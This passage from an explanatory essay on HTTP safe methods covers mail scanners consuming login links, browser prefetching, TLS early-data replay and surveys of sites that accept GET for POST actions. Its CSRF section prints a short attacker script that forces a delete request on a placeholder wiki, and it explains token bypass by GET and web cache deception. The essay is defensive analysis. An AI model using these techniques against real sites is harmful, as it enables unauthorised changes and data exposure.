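The first line was already in use, and it had the same problem as links in the text, because anti-spam software often fetched the address. The second line tells the mail program that it can unsubscribe the reader with a POST. When the reader presses the program's own "Unsubscribe" button, the program sends this:

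```
POST /unsubscribe/8c41e7 HTTP/1.1
Host: lists.example.org
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded
Content-Length: 26

List-Unsubscribe=One-Click
```

The server can now tell the two kinds of visit apart. It answers a GET to the address with a confirmation page, and it treats a POST with this body as a finished decision. A scanner that fetches the address gets the page and changes nothing. (A server that removes the subscriber on either method is no better off than before.)

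The request body is always the same because the address comes from an email, which anyone can send. If the sender could also choose the body, a spammer could make the reader's mail program submit a form on another website. Levine and Herkula also require the mail program to leave out cookies, which could link the request to the reader's earlier browsing. They recommend that the address contain a code that is hard to forge. Otherwise, a spammer could insert another list's unsubscribe address, and readers who reported the spam would be removed from that list. The email also needs a valid DKIM signature, a cryptographic stamp from the sending domain, that covers both header lines.

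A scanner can technically send the POST too, but under the standard a mail receiver "MUST NOT" do so without the user's consent. The standard doesn't specify how to obtain that consent.

Google has the clearest requirement of the large mail providers. Its *Email sender guidelines* require anyone who sends more than 5,000 messages a day to include one-click unsubscribing in marketing and subscribed messages, and they name both headers. The only penalty that the *Email sender guidelines FAQ* lists for leaving it out is the loss of help with delivery problems, while some other violations can get messages rejected or sent to the spam folder.

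Mailgun, an email delivery company, lists RFC 8058 as a Yahoo requirement, but Suped, another vendor, says that Yahoo "highly" recommends it and also accepts an email address for unsubscribe requests. According to Mailgun's comparison, Microsoft and Apple ask only for a visible unsubscribe link or option.

RFC 8058 covers only the email header, so it doesn't protect the ordinary unsubscribe link at the bottom of the newsletter. According to Suped, Yahoo also requires a visible link in the text. That link still needs to open a page with a button.

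### Login links used up before the user clicks

Many sites let people log in without a password by emailing them a link that works once. The server marks the code in the link as used after the first visit, so someone who finds the email later can't use it to log in. Sites use similar links to reset passwords and to confirm new accounts.

When a user of the harbour wiki asks for such a link, the wiki emails one ending in `/login?token=d94b02`. The scanner opens it before the email arrives. The server accepts the token, marks it as used, and returns a new session cookie. This briefly logs the scanner in as the user, though the scanner doesn't use the cookie. A minute later the user clicks the same link and gets an error, and requesting a new link leads to the same result.

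Supabase provides login systems to developers, and its *Email Templates* documentation names Safe Links as a cause of the error "Token has expired or is invalid". A bug report for Drupal, a widely used content management system, described the same failure with Outlook.com, Microsoft's consumer mail service, whose BingPreview crawler was visiting login links and locking people out of their accounts. In *"Link protect" software breaks passwordless auth*, a developer suspected that a customer's software from another company, Mimecast, was using up the links, and learned that the login provider, Auth0, had no way to let a link work twice.

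The failure may go unnoticed with confirmation links, as with the faulty mailing list that Jacobs described. If someone signs up with a stranger's address and the stranger's employer scans the email, the scanner may confirm the account on the stranger's behalf.

Some developers tried to recognise the scanners. One, who posts as colas, first added `rel="nofollow"`, a hint for search engines, but this had no effect. He then refused requests whose user agent, the text a program sends to identify itself, contained "BingPreview" or "Slackbot". Like the `X-moz` block of 2005, this works only on programs that identify themselves accurately.

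### The page with a button

A sturdier repair is to let the emailed link open a page that contains a form, and to use up the code only when the user submits it:

```
<form method="post" action="/login">
  <input type="hidden" name="token" value="d94b02">
  <button>Log in</button>
</form>
```

The scanner's GET now retrieves the form without using the code. Users have to click once more, and some developers tried to avoid the extra click with a script that submitted the form as soon as the page opened. This worked for a while because most scanners didn't run scripts. In June 2019 a developer reported success with it under *Do mail servers follow links in emails*, a question on a security forum. Two years later another user commented there that Microsoft seemed to be running a scanner that submitted such forms automatically.

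In *Shifting Cyber Norms* on berthub.eu, Bert Hubert describes a problem on a site he built for following the Dutch parliament. A user could no longer log in because every login link had already been used. Hubert's server log showed a POST from a Microsoft address, with a user agent he calls fake, followed by the user's own failed attempt. A mail scanner had opened the link and run the JavaScript, which sent the POST.

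Hubert calls this a strong violation of the norm that software doesn't send a POST just to see what happens. He also concedes that there may be "some truth" in a more charitable reading, in which his own page caused the change in response to a GET. That reading seems to me the stronger one as far as the site's role is concerned, because a form that submits itself logs the user in as soon as the link is opened, without anyone deciding to log in. But Microsoft also took a risk that a scanner limited to GET requests avoids, since a POST is a sign that something may change.

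Scanners apparently don't press buttons yet, and Descope, another login provider, relies on this. Its software tries to detect scanners and shows them a screen with a button, which they "typically won't interact with", while people it recognises as genuine go straight through. Supabase also suggests a page with a button, but its button is an ordinary link to the original confirmation address. This stops a scanner that opens only the links in the email. A scanner that also followed links on the page would use up the code with a second GET, but a form that sends a POST would stop that scanner too.

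Hubert expects scanners to start pressing buttons sooner or later and advises developers to make links that still work after a scanner has used them. Reusable links are somewhat less secure, because they also work for anyone else who gets hold of the email. Supabase's other suggestion is to email a six-digit code that the user types into the site, so a scanner can open every link in the email without logging anyone in.

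### Link previews

Chat programs can cause the same failure without looking for malware. When someone pastes a link into a conversation, many of these programs fetch the page to show a preview. Microsoft's *Use Link Preview in Outlook.com and Outlook on the web* describes an equivalent email feature, which is on by default and shows a box with the page's title, a thumbnail image and a description.

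A chat program has to request a linked page to show its title in a preview. If a user pastes a one-time login link into a chat to ask a colleague why it isn't working, the preview may use up the link before the colleague clicks it. An "Unsubscribe" link in a forwarded newsletter carries the same risk. Requiring a button press on a confirmation page protects against both, since the preview then shows only that page's title.

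Few cases are documented, however. The rule colas posted blocks Slackbot, which fetches links for the workplace chat service Slack, but he mentions only BingPreview in his account of lost login links.

### How often scanners click

No published study seems to measure how often mail scanners open links, or how many of those visits change something. The reports above come from people who had a problem, so they show that the failure happens but give little indication of how common it is. The rate is difficult to measure from the sender's side because, as Levine and Herkula point out, a sender has no mechanical way to tell an automatic request from a reader's click.

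Phishing researchers have the same difficulty. *What You See is Not What You Get* (2023) compared how often people clicked an email link shown as a bare address, a button or linked text. The researchers gave each recipient a unique ID and recorded every visit to that person's link. They noted that mail services can generate "open/click events that are not performed by the user", but gave no rate. They had no reason to think that these events affected the three groups differently. If they are right, the comparison between groups still holds, but the total number of clicks may overstate how many people fell for the email. Hubert mentions the extreme case, a company phishing test in which every employee appears to have clicked every link.

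## Prefetching in today's browsers

Browsers now mostly let sites choose which links are prefetched, whereas mail scanners open links without the site's permission. Since early 2023, sites have been able to specify these links through the Speculation Rules API. Chrome, Edge and Opera support it, Safari has it only behind a test setting, and Firefox doesn't support it. By March 2025, over 8% of page visits in Chrome relied on it, according to WordPress' *Speculative Loading in 6.8* (2025).

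### How a site asks for prefetching

WHATWG, the group that maintains the HTML standard, defines speculation rules as the way developers tell the browser which pages they think are worth loading early. A developer writes the rules in JSON, a common data format, and puts them in the page or in a separate file that a response header points to. A rule can list addresses one by one or describe links by a pattern. For articles on the harbour wiki, it might look like this:

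```
<script type="speculationrules">
{ "prefetch": [{
    "where": { "and": [
      { "href_matches": "/page/*" },
      { "not": { "href_matches": "/page/*/delete" } }
    ]},
    "eagerness": "moderate"
}]}
</script>
```

This is a request for the browser to prefetch any link whose address begins with `/page/`, except the "Delete" links. The browser may ignore it, as Chrome does, for example, when the user has turned on data saving.

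Browsers still load some pages before the user requests them. Chrome, for example, does this if it is more than 50% confident that the user is typing a particular page's address, as Chrome for Developers' *Prerender pages in Chrome for instant page navigations* (2022) explains. But browsers don't automatically prefetch arbitrary links on a page because, as dri.es' *Speculation Rules changed my mind about prefetching* notes, a prefetch of `/logout` would sign the visitor out.

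The eagerness setting tells the browser how strong a sign of interest to wait for. Chrome currently interprets the four levels like this:

| Level | With a mouse | On a phone |
|---|---|---|
| conservative | the user presses the button on a link | the user touches a link |
| moderate | the pointer rests on a link for 200 milliseconds | half a second after scrolling stops, for fairly large links near the last touch |
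| eager | the pointer rests on a link for 10 milliseconds | 50 milliseconds after a link comes into view |
| immediate | as soon as the browser reads the rule | the same |

By default, rules that use a pattern are conservative and rules that list addresses are immediate. At the three lower levels, Chrome holds only two prefetched pages at a time, and a third replaces the oldest. Removing a page saves memory in the browser but doesn't undo anything the request did on the server.

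For Mozilla's prefetching in 2005, the page's author marked each link. A pattern like `/page/*` also covers links the developer has never looked at, so the developer has to think of the exceptions. A prefetch within the same site carries the session cookie, so if the wiki's developer forgets the `not` line, a logged-in user who rests the mouse on "Delete" for a fifth of a second deletes the harbour page.

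Links to other sites are less risky to prefetch because the browser does so only if the user has no cookies for the other site, as MDN's *Speculation Rules API* explains. MDN gives privacy as the reason, but the restriction also stops one site from using a prefetch to delete things from a visitor's account on another.

### Prefetching and prerendering

To prefetch a page, the browser sends a single GET request for it and keeps the response in memory. It doesn't load the page's images or run its scripts until the user opens the page. To prerender a page, the browser loads the whole page, including images, and runs its scripts in an invisible tab. If the user then clicks a link to the page, the browser swaps in that tab, and the page appears almost instantly.

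Prerendering creates additional risks because it runs the page's scripts. If the wiki counts readers with a script, a prefetch doesn't change the count, but a prerender adds a reader who may never open the page. Scripts that record advertising views have the same problem. A developer can avoid this by making the script wait for an event that the browser fires when the user opens the page. The browser also delays or blocks the most intrusive features. It delays notifications and requests for the user's location until the page is visible, and if a script asks the user to confirm something, the browser immediately returns "no" without showing a dialog.

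Chrome's developers are working on an intermediate option that would prerender a page only as far as its first script. By default, a site can prerender only its own pages, and browsers don't yet allow prerendering across sites.

### The Sec-Purpose header

The browser labels these early requests. If the user rests the mouse on a link to the lighthouse page, the wiki's server receives roughly this:

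```
GET /page/lighthouse HTTP/1.1
Host: wiki.example.org
Cookie: session=7f3a9c
Sec-Purpose: prefetch
```

For a prerender, the value of the `Sec-Purpose` header is `prefetch;prerender`. In the draft definition that van Kesteren reviewed for the Fetch Standard, the header marks a request with a purpose "other than requesting the resource for immediate use by the user". It serves the same function as the `X-moz` header, which 37signals used to block the accelerator. Mozilla replaced `X-moz` with the new header in Firefox 115, and *Intent to Ship* (Chromestatus, 2025) announced that Chrome would drop its own older equivalent.

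A server can refuse a prefetch by returning an error such as 503. The browser then discards the attempt and sends an ordinary request if the user clicks. According to MDN, it is usually better to accept the prefetch and use a script to delay the action until the user opens the page. A server that ignores the header marking a prefetch handles the request like any other GET. Both methods therefore require the developer to know that the address is dangerous, and a developer who knows this could often just switch the link to POST.

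### Addresses that are unsafe to prefetch

MDN's documentation warns developers about six kinds of address. Each one makes the server do something as soon as the request arrives:

| Address | What goes wrong after an unwanted prefetch |
|---|---|
| Sign out | The server ends the session, and the user has to log in again. |
| Switch language | The server saves the new setting, and later pages appear in a language the user only pointed at. |
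| Add to cart | A product the user never chose is in the cart, and may end up in the order. |
| Sign-in step that sends a text message | The user's phone receives a login code that nobody asked for. |
| Page that counts towards an allowance | The reader loses one of the month's free articles, or a timer on paid minutes starts. |
| Page that records an advertising conversion | The advertiser's figures include a sale or sign-up that didn't happen. |

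Several of these are action links like those Google Web Accelerator triggered in 2005. MDN suggests looking for others in the site's robots.txt file, since site owners often list pages for logged-in users there to keep crawlers out.

Prefetching can also show users outdated pages, even when every GET on the site is safe. Suppose the browser prerenders an empty cart while a shopper is looking at a product. If the shopper adds the product and opens the cart, the browser shows the empty version. A user who logs in on one tab can likewise see a logged-out page in another. Chrome keeps prefetched pages for five minutes, so a page can be that far out of date. To prevent this, the server can have the browser discard its prepared pages whenever something changes, or the page can refresh itself when it opens.

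### WordPress

WordPress, the most widely used software for running websites, turned on prefetching by default in version 6.8 in 2025. It uses conservative eagerness and covers the public part of each site, but excludes logged-in users and links with a query string. The feature is also off on sites whose ordinary page addresses use query strings, where a query string wouldn't help distinguish links that perform actions from links to articles.

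The second exclusion is for what the WordPress developers call "action URLs", such as a link that puts a product in a cart. They call such links an antipattern because GET requests are supposed to be "idempotent", by which they evidently mean safe. The question-mark rule is the same one Google used in 2005, and it still misses action URLs that have no question mark. A plugin that uses addresses like `/cart/add/121` has to exclude them itself, which takes a few lines of code.

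WordPress considers the gap tolerable at the conservative level because a user who has started to click is "almost guaranteed" to open the page. That is a little optimistic, since users opened the prefetched page 94% of the time when Cloudflare tried conservative prefetching on its own documentation in July 2024. Links with a JavaScript confirmation are a particular problem. The browser sends a conservative prefetch when the user presses the mouse button, but the confirmation appears only when the user releases it. By the time the user can choose "Cancel", the server may have carried out the action. Excluding logged-in users is therefore the more important protection, since most "Delete" links require a login.

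Before the release, over 50,000 sites had tried the feature as a plugin. Their pass rate for Largest Contentful Paint (LCP), a measure of how soon the biggest item on the screen appears, improved by about 1.9% at the median. But the plugin prerendered pages at moderate eagerness by default, so the more cautious setting in version 6.8 probably improves LCP less.

In *Add speculative loading support*, WordPress developers discussed the risks and agreed that "immediate" eagerness would make them worse, so WordPress doesn't allow that level for its main rule. The defaults may still become more aggressive. In *Speculative Loading*, WordPress developer westonruter proposes moderate eagerness for sites that use caching, but the ticket still needs a second opinion and isn't tied to a particular release. A July 2026 change, described in *Allow configuration of speculative loading defaults via env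 variables and constants* (westonruter, 2026), lets a hosting company switch the default to prerendering or to a higher level of eagerness.

### Cloudflare's Speed Brain

Cloudflare runs a network of servers that stand between websites and their visitors and keep copies of pages. In September 2024 it introduced Speed Brain, which adds a speculation rule to a site's responses without any work by the site's owner. *Introducing Speed Brain*, by Krivit, Ahmad and Woodhead, reported that the feature was already running on tens of millions of domains.

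The rule covers every link within the site, including "Delete" links and addresses with a question mark. Cloudflare keeps these prefetches from reaching the site's own server, so they can't make it sign anyone out or delete anything. When a user presses the mouse button on a link, the browser sends Cloudflare a GET with the Sec-Purpose header. If Cloudflare has a stored copy of the page, it returns the copy. If not, it answers with a 503 and doesn't forward the request. Cloudflare also excludes addresses that run Workers, small programs that site owners can place on its network, because a Worker could count page views.

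This is a much stronger safeguard than looking for a question mark, because Cloudflare doesn't need to guess what a link does. However, Speed Brain can't speed up pages that the server builds separately for each visitor.

Krivit and colleagues report that LCP was about 45% (roughly 0.9 to 1.1 seconds) lower on successful prefetches than on ordinary page loads on the same domains. These figures are for the 75th percentile, the value that three quarters of page loads stay within. Part of the difference is probably due to caching, because every successful prefetch comes from Cloudflare's store, while an ordinary load may have to wait for the site's own server. The gain also applies to few page loads, since only around 1% of requests were prefetches (it is unclear from the wording whether that means all requests for pages or only the cached ones).

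In its 2024 announcement, Cloudflare promised more aggressive prefetching and prerendering during 2025. Its *Speed Brain* documentation, updated in June 2026, still describes the conservative rule and the same two safeguards. Speed Brain is on by default for the free plan, but paid customers have to turn it on.

### Who opts in, and what still fails

In 2005 a site could not control whether Google's program prefetched its links. Today the browser needs a rule from the site, whose owner is far more likely to know what its links do. In practice, though, WordPress or Cloudflare often supplies the rule, and the owner may never have heard of it. Shopify's *Speed up navigations with the Speculation Rules API* describes another such default, which has covered most of the shops on its platform since June 2025. WordPress and Cloudflare need general exclusions because they don't know every link on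 their customers' sites.

A browser can also change when it prefetches under a setting that a site has already chosen. Until August 2025, Chrome on phones waited for a touch before prefetching a link at the "moderate" level. It then began to prefetch links that had only come into view and seemed likely to be clicked, a change Denicola (2025) had announced that June in *Web-Facing Change PSA*. Sites that had chosen "moderate" because it waited for a touch now received requests earlier, even though they had changed nothing. The specification allows this because it leaves the exact definitions of the levels "vague", according to a companion notice, also titled *Web-Facing Change PSA*.

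Most reported faults with Speed Brain have involved errors and failed actions. On 24 September 2024, Cloudflare switched off the beta worldwide, 16 minutes after announcing that it was investigating a problem for customers of Pages, its web hosting service. *Cloudflare Speed Brain possibly impacting Cloudflare Pages* (eva2000, 2024) preserves the status notice. Speed Brain still doesn't work with sites on Pages' `pages.dev` addresses. IsDown's *Outage in Cloudflare* (2024) records a 27-minute incident in November 2024 with too many 503 errors.

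Even the 503s that Speed Brain returns intentionally cause trouble. In *yo'av, I know this isnt Zaraz related*, a site owner describes spending hours trying to find out why nearly 1% of page requests were failing. The failures were prefetches that Speed Brain had refused, and they made genuine 503 errors impossible to pick out in the statistics. Cloudflare has said that a separate status code for refused prefetches would be less confusing.

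*How Cloudflare’s Speed Brain Gave Us a WordPress Headache*, by the web design company NW Design, describes a site where updating plugins and deleting posts stopped working until the company turned Speed Brain off. Speed Brain's design doesn't explain this, because a refused prefetch should have no effect on the click that follows, but the timing of the fix suggests that Speed Brain was involved.

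Also, only the site that contains the link has to opt in. A page can direct its visitors' browsers to prefetch from another site, which then has to answer the requests. *Speculation rules for evil* warns that this could put a heavy load on online shops, where searches and add-to-cart links often can't be served from a cache. The rule about cookies protects the visitor's account on the other site but doesn't reduce this load.

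### Replayed requests in TLS 1.3

An attacker can also resend a GET that the user sent only once. This risk comes from early data, an optional feature of TLS 1.3, the current version of the encryption used for HTTPS. Normally a browser and server exchange messages to set up encryption before the browser sends its first request. If the two have connected recently, early data lets the browser send the request with its opening message, which saves a round trip. In 2017 about 40% of the secure connections that Cloudflare handled came from returning visitors.

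An attacker on the network can copy the encrypted request and resend it. The attacker can't read it, but the server may decrypt it and carry it out a second time. Cloudflare's *Introducing Zero Round Trip Time Resumption (0-RTT)* (2017) gives the example of a bank that receives the instruction to "pay $1000 to Craig" several times. TLS 1.3 requires servers to look for duplicates, but a large site has many servers, and one may accept a copy of a request that another has already handled.

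*Using Early Data in HTTP* (Thomson, Nottingham and Tarreau, 2018; RFC 8470) sets the rules for this. Unless it has other information, a client may send safe methods in early data but "MUST NOT" send unsafe ones. Idempotence isn't enough, because an attacker can choose when to replay the request. In the notation used earlier, *r*(*r*(*s*)) = *r*(*s*) covers only a repeat that follows immediately. If another change *q* comes in between, *r*(*q*(*r*(*s*))) can differ from *q*(*r*(*s*)). For example, a user deletes the harbour page, another editor restores it, and a replay of the first request deletes it again. A safe request avoids this problem because it changes nothing, no matter when it arrives.

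Thomson and colleagues concede that this relies on sites following the rule, because "some resources produce side effects with safe methods". Often only the site's own server knows which ones. They therefore give it a way to refuse. A machine in between, such as one of Cloudflare's, adds a header when it passes on a request that arrived as early data:

```
GET /page/harbour/delete HTTP/1.1
Host: wiki.example.org
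Cookie: session=7f3a9c
Early-Data: 1
```

The wiki can answer with status 425, "Too Early", and the browser resends the request once the encryption is fully set up. As with Sec-Purpose, this works only if the wiki's developer has added a check for the header.

Some operators don't want to depend on that. In 2017 Cloudflare accepted early data only for GET requests without a query string, as a precaution for sites that couldn't handle replays. *Early Data (0-RTT) Advanced*, a documentation page from Akamai, another large delivery network, describes the same default and gives the reason that such requests are the most likely to be harmless. The limit has the same gap as the question-mark rules for prefetching, so it wouldn't stop a replay of the request above. It also slows down harmless requests that have query strings, such as searches.

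Cloudflare later left more of the choice to sites. It had turned early data on for all free sites in 2017, but Ghedini explains in *Even faster connection establishment with QUIC 0-RTT resumption* that it is now off by default because even "innocuous-looking" requests can have side effects. Cloudflare's *0-RTT Connection Resumption* documentation now lists GET, HEAD and OPTIONS as supported methods and doesn't mention a limit on query strings. Akamai's customers can lift the limit for chosen addresses and even allow POST or DELETE, but they are responsible for making sure their servers can handle a repeated payment.

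## How many sites accept a GET in place of a POST

Crawling, prefetching and early data are harmless only if sites require POST for actions that change something. In *When POST Becomes GET*, Golinelli, Hannachi and Crispo (2026) recorded POST requests on the 10,000 most popular sites, resent each one as a GET and compared the responses. On 407 sites, or 4.1%, at least one GET got the same response as the POST it replaced. These sites accept either method for some request, but the GET does not necessarily change anything.

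### Sending a POST again as a GET

The researchers took their sites from the 7 May 2026 version of Tranco, a website ranking made for research. An automated Chromium browser visited up to ten pages of each site without logging in. It filled in forms with harmless made-up values, clicked some of the buttons and recorded every resulting POST, including those sent by scripts in the background. To avoid doing damage, the crawler skipped file uploads and any button or address whose wording suggested that it deleted something, changed data or signed the user out.

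Suppose that the harbour wiki has a search form that uses POST. For that form, the server receives three requests in all:

```
POST /search                            (body: text=harbour&sort=newest)
GET  /search?text=harbour&sort=newest
GET  /search
```

The second request has the same parameters as the first, moved from the body to the query string. The third is a control with no parameters. If the wiki returns search results for the first two and an empty form for the third, it must have read the parameters from the query string. If all three responses match, the wiki may be ignoring the parameters.

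Two responses matched if they had the same status code and a structural similarity of at least 0.95. For web pages, this score compares the sequence of HTML tags and ignores the text, so a new timestamp doesn't prevent a match. But the score also can't distinguish "Page deleted" from "You may not delete this page" if a site puts both messages in the same template. For JSON responses, the score compares field names, and two responses didn't match if they had different values for a field such as "success".

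The comparisons gave four classes:

| Class | GET with parameters | GET without parameters | Requests |
|---|---|---|---|
| A, strong | matches the POST | differs | 1,228 (8.6%) |
| B, ambiguous | matches the POST | matches the POST | 1,782 (12.5%) |
| C, baseline collision | differs | matches the POST | 242 (1.7%) |
| D, not interchangeable | differs | differs | 10,992 (77.2%) |

Golinelli and colleagues based their main figures on class A alone. Without the control, they would have counted class B too and reported well over twice as many requests.

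They also checked 60 results by hand, half from class A and half from class D. All 30 GETs in class A had the same outcome as the original POST, and none of the 30 in class D did. For one class A request, the control also seemed to match, so the request probably belonged in class B. The class A result is reassuring, but even if nearly 10% of the GETs in that class had a different outcome from the POST, a sample of 30 would miss all of them about one time in 20.

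### 407 sites and what they accepted

The crawler recorded POST requests on only 3,200 of the 10,000 sites, and it could convert and resend at least one on 2,734 of them. The 407 sites are therefore 4.1% of all those tested, 12.7% of those with a recorded POST and 14.9% of those with a resent one. The 4.1% figure counts the 6,800 sites with no recorded POST as if they had passed, although many of them must have forms that the crawler never reached. More than a quarter of the recorded requests had a body in a format that the software couldn't convert.

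Search was the most common purpose of the class A requests, at 30.9%. Another 15.1% were for analytics or tracking, 9.9% went to programming interfaces, and 8.9% related to logging in. A search that works with both methods is not a fault, because it changes nothing and, by Jacobs's test, is a question that belongs in a GET.

Golinelli and colleagues call a broader group of labels potentially security-relevant. It covers logins, account settings, shopping carts, new content and administration pages. Requests with these labels made up 31.5% of class A and 32.5% of all the resent requests. About 8% of them worked as a GET, compared with nearly 10% of the less sensitive requests, so developers seem to have been only slightly stricter where it mattered more. But the labels come from keywords in addresses, parameter names and responses. Since the crawler wasn't logged in, an "account settings"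 request may have reached only a login page.

### How one address comes to accept both methods

An address accepts both GET and POST if the server runs the same code for each and that code can read its input from either the query string or the request body. Programs in plain PHP, a common language for websites, often meet both conditions. A PHP script normally runs for either method unless the developer adds a check. PHP puts query string parameters in `$_GET` and parameters from a POST form in `$_POST`, but a script can read both from `$_REQUEST`.

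The wiki's code for deleting a page could begin with either of these lines:

```
if ($_REQUEST['do'] == 'delete') delete_page($_GET['title']);  // GET or POST
if ($_POST['do'] == 'delete')    delete_page($_GET['title']);  // POST only
```

A GET for `/page?title=Harbour&do=delete` deletes the page if the code uses the first line, but not if it uses the second. The developer who wrote the first line may never have thought about GET. The wiki's own form sends a POST and works as intended, so ordinary testing doesn't reveal the problem.

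Golinelli and colleagues compared popular web frameworks, the ready-made code that developers build sites on, and found that the defaults vary:

| | An address accepts any method by default | The developer chooses the methods |
|---|---|---|
| Offers merged input | plain PHP | Laravel, Rails, Flask, Sinatra, Gin |
| Keeps query string and body apart | Django | Next.js, SvelteKit |

In Django, a GET can reach code written for a POST, but that code gets no input if it reads from the request body. In Rails or Laravel, a GET can reach the same code as a POST only if the developer registers the address for both methods, and the code then handles input from either in the same way. In Spring, a Java framework, the general `@RequestMapping` may accept every method, whereas `@PostMapping` accepts only POST. The server software Nginx, which can sit in front of the application, also has a setting that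 changes a request's method before passing it on.

Sometimes designers intend both methods to work. GraphQL, a query language for programming interfaces, allows read-only queries by GET or POST, but its draft rules for HTTP forbid using GET for a "mutation", its term for a change. SPARQL, a query language for linked data, makes the same distinction. Sites that follow these rules can fall into class A and still comply with the HTTP standard, which requires site owners only to disable unsafe actions for GET.

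### Actions the crawler avoided

Golinelli and colleagues did not verify that any of the 1,228 requests changed something on the server, which is hard to do from outside. Pellegrino, Johns and colleagues explained in *Deemon* (2017) that an outside tester sees only the responses, and pages contain so much changing content that comparing them is an unreliable way to tell whether the stored data has changed.

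Their own tool, Deemon, avoids this by running a copy of the application on the tester's machine. It repeats a user's recorded actions and logs the program's function calls and database operations to work out which requests changed the data. It then resends those requests as an attacker would and uses snapshots to undo the effects. Since routine changes such as log entries don't matter for security, Deemon is built on the assumption that the important changes are the rarer ones. It found 14 previously unknown flaws in four of the ten open-source applications tested. A survey of 10,000 live sites can't use this method because the researchers don't have the sites' code.

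The survey also left out many of the requests that would have been most informative. On the harbour wiki, the crawler would have tested the search form but not the "Delete" button, which appears only after login and has a label that the crawler avoids. A request that did change something could also fail the comparison because of that change. For example, if the crawler signs up for a newsletter with a POST and then repeats the request as a GET, the server may reply that the address is already on the list. The 4.1% is probably too low an estimate of how many sites accept either method, and it doesn't measure how many let a GET change something.

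A site in class A does not necessarily publish an action link either. The researchers' software constructed addresses that may not appear on any page, and a crawler or prefetcher that only follows links would never request those that don't. An attacker can still request them, as can any program that composes its own addresses. This is relevant to the edits that OpenAI's agents made to DseWiki, a German wiki, in 2026.

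### Cross-site request forgery and SameSite cookies

An attacker can exploit such an address through cross-site request forgery, in which a hostile page makes the victim's browser send the request with the victim's cookie. According to Pellegrino and colleagues, the request must cause a change that matters for security, the attacker must know every value in it, and the server must process it as the logged-in user's own.

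A secret token in the form defeats the attack through the second condition. A newer defence, the SameSite attribute, works on the third by limiting when the browser sends the cookie. The wiki sets it at login:

```
Set-Cookie: session=7f3a9c; SameSite=Lax
```

With `None`, the browser sends the cookie with every request to the wiki, even one caused by another site's page. With `Strict`, it never sends the cookie with a request from another site, so a user who follows a link to the wiki from a search engine arrives logged out. With `Lax`, according to the web security company PortSwigger, the browser sends the cookie with a request from another site only if the request uses GET and is a top-level navigation. In a top-level navigation, the browser opens the page itself instead of loading a picture or frame inside another page.

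Khodayari and Pellegrino, in *The State of the SameSite*, list the cases in more detail, including these:

| What another site's page does | Browser sends the wiki's Lax cookie |
|---|---|
| Contains a link that the user clicks | yes |
| Runs a script that opens the wiki's address | yes |
| Submits a form by GET | yes |
| Submits a form by POST | no |
| Loads the address as an image, script or frame | no |

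Since July 2020, Chrome has treated a cookie without the SameSite attribute as `Lax`. For the first two minutes after a site sets such a cookie, however, a POST from another site can still carry it, because some login services depend on this. In early 2021, Firefox and Safari still defaulted to `None`.

The trick from 2005, an image whose address is really a "Delete" link, no longer works against a Lax cookie. But the attacker's page can send the whole browser to that address:

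```
<script>
location = "https://wiki.example.org/page?title=Harbour&do=delete";
</script>
```

The request is a GET and a top-level navigation, so the browser attaches the cookie. If the wiki's code uses `$_REQUEST`, the request deletes the harbour page before the victim can react.

A more recent defence has the same gap. Browsers now add Fetch Metadata headers, which tell the server whether a request came from another site. In *Fetch Me If You Can*, Bernardo, Ploner and colleagues (2026) analysed the standard policies that servers can build on these headers. The policy they consider a good balance between security and functionality rejects requests from other sites unless they are top-level or framed page loads by GET or HEAD. It would block the image but not the script above. Their formal analysis excludes state-changing GETs from the definition of forgery because such requests already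 violate the HTTP standard. That is reasonable for an analysis of the policies, but a site owner who relies on the result has to be sure that the site has no such requests. Bernardo and colleagues found the policies on only 0.23% of the top million sites.

### Tokens that protect only the POST

Frameworks typically check the secret token only for POST and other unsafe methods, since a GET shouldn't need protection. If the code that handles a POST also runs for a GET, an attacker may be able to avoid the check by sending a GET instead.

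Golinelli and colleagues tested this on 115 of their class A requests, from 46 sites, that included a parameter or header with a name like "csrf" or "nonce". They sent each POST again without the token and with a wrong one, then did the same with the GET. In seven cases, on two sites, the server rejected the POST without a valid token but accepted the GET without one.

In another 78 cases, on 25 sites, the server accepted both methods with an invalid token. These cases may mean little, because some of the names the researchers searched for, such as "state", have other uses, and a site has less reason to check a token when nobody is logged in. Most of the remaining tests failed or were inconclusive, and the server clearly rejected the GET for its invalid token in only one case. The researchers didn't check whether any of the seven requests changed data or whether another site could trigger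 them, so they describe a gap in the defences rather than a working attack.

They also tested whether caches would store the responses. In an attack called web cache deception, the attacker alters an address, for example by adding `.css`, so that a cache treats a personal page as a file that is the same for everyone. If the victim opens the altered address, the cache stores the victim's page and the attacker can fetch it. Caches mostly don't store responses to POST requests, so making a response available by GET as well can expose it to this attack. Altering the address caused caches to store 56 of the 1,228 responses, on nine sites. Another 136, on 50 sites, were cacheable without any alteration. The crawler had no accounts, so the tests didn't involve real users' data.

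### State changes by GET on logged-in pages

Nobody seems to have counted action links on the pages that people see after logging in. The closest evidence comes from studies of forgery, which counted how many state-changing requests use GET as intended by the site:

| Sample | State-changing requests | By GET |
|---|---|---|
| 51 sites, from 2017 | 924 | 121 (13%) |
| 23 sites, from 2019 | 67 | 5 (7%) |
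| 922 of the top 1,000 sites, published 2022 | 6,951 | 721 (10%) |

The first sample comes from the training data for Mitch, a machine-learning tool that Focardi, Rabitti, Tolomei and two colleagues built to find forgery flaws. People used the sites while logged in and labelled the sensitive requests by hand. Compagna, Jonker and colleagues reanalysed that data in *A preliminary study on the adoption and effectiveness of SameSite cookies* and added the second sample, which they had also labelled by hand. They report that about 30% of the GETs in the first sample were for signing out. An unwanted sign-out is a nuisance but loses no data, so the share of GETs that could do lasting damage is smaller than 13%.

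The third sample is the crawl by Khodayari and Pellegrino, who instead searched pages for forms with an anti-forgery token and treated the token as a sign that the form changes something. This allowed a much larger sample, but a site may also put a token in a search form, and the crawl would have missed ordinary "Delete" links because they aren't forms.

Khodayari and Pellegrino went further than the 2026 survey by demonstrating actual changes. They picked up to three of the GET requests from each of the 88 sites that had any, 264 in all, and could forge seven, on four sites. On the art site Pixiv, an attacker could delete a user's sketches. They then took a POST from each of 602 sites and sent it as a GET, much as Golinelli and colleagues later did. Nine of these requests could be forged, on six sites. They allowed an attacker to edit a film watchlist on IMDb, for example, or to modify a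 user's invoices on PayPal. (The researchers say they tested one request per site, which doesn't fit with nine successes on six sites, so the rate of 1.5% that they give is a little doubtful. By site, it is 1%.)

That 1% is lower than the 14.9% of sites where Golinelli and colleagues could resend a POST and found one that worked as a GET, but the two figures measure different things. The 1% counts only sites with a state-changing request, a missing or faulty token check and a working attack, whereas a search form is enough for a site to count toward the 14.9%. The earlier researchers also tried roughly one request per site, while Golinelli and colleagues tried about five on average.

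These figures are old, and some of the sites have probably fixed their flaws since. But Bernardo and colleagues still cited the roughly 10% figure in 2026, which suggests no better one has replaced it.

### The chance of meeting such a site

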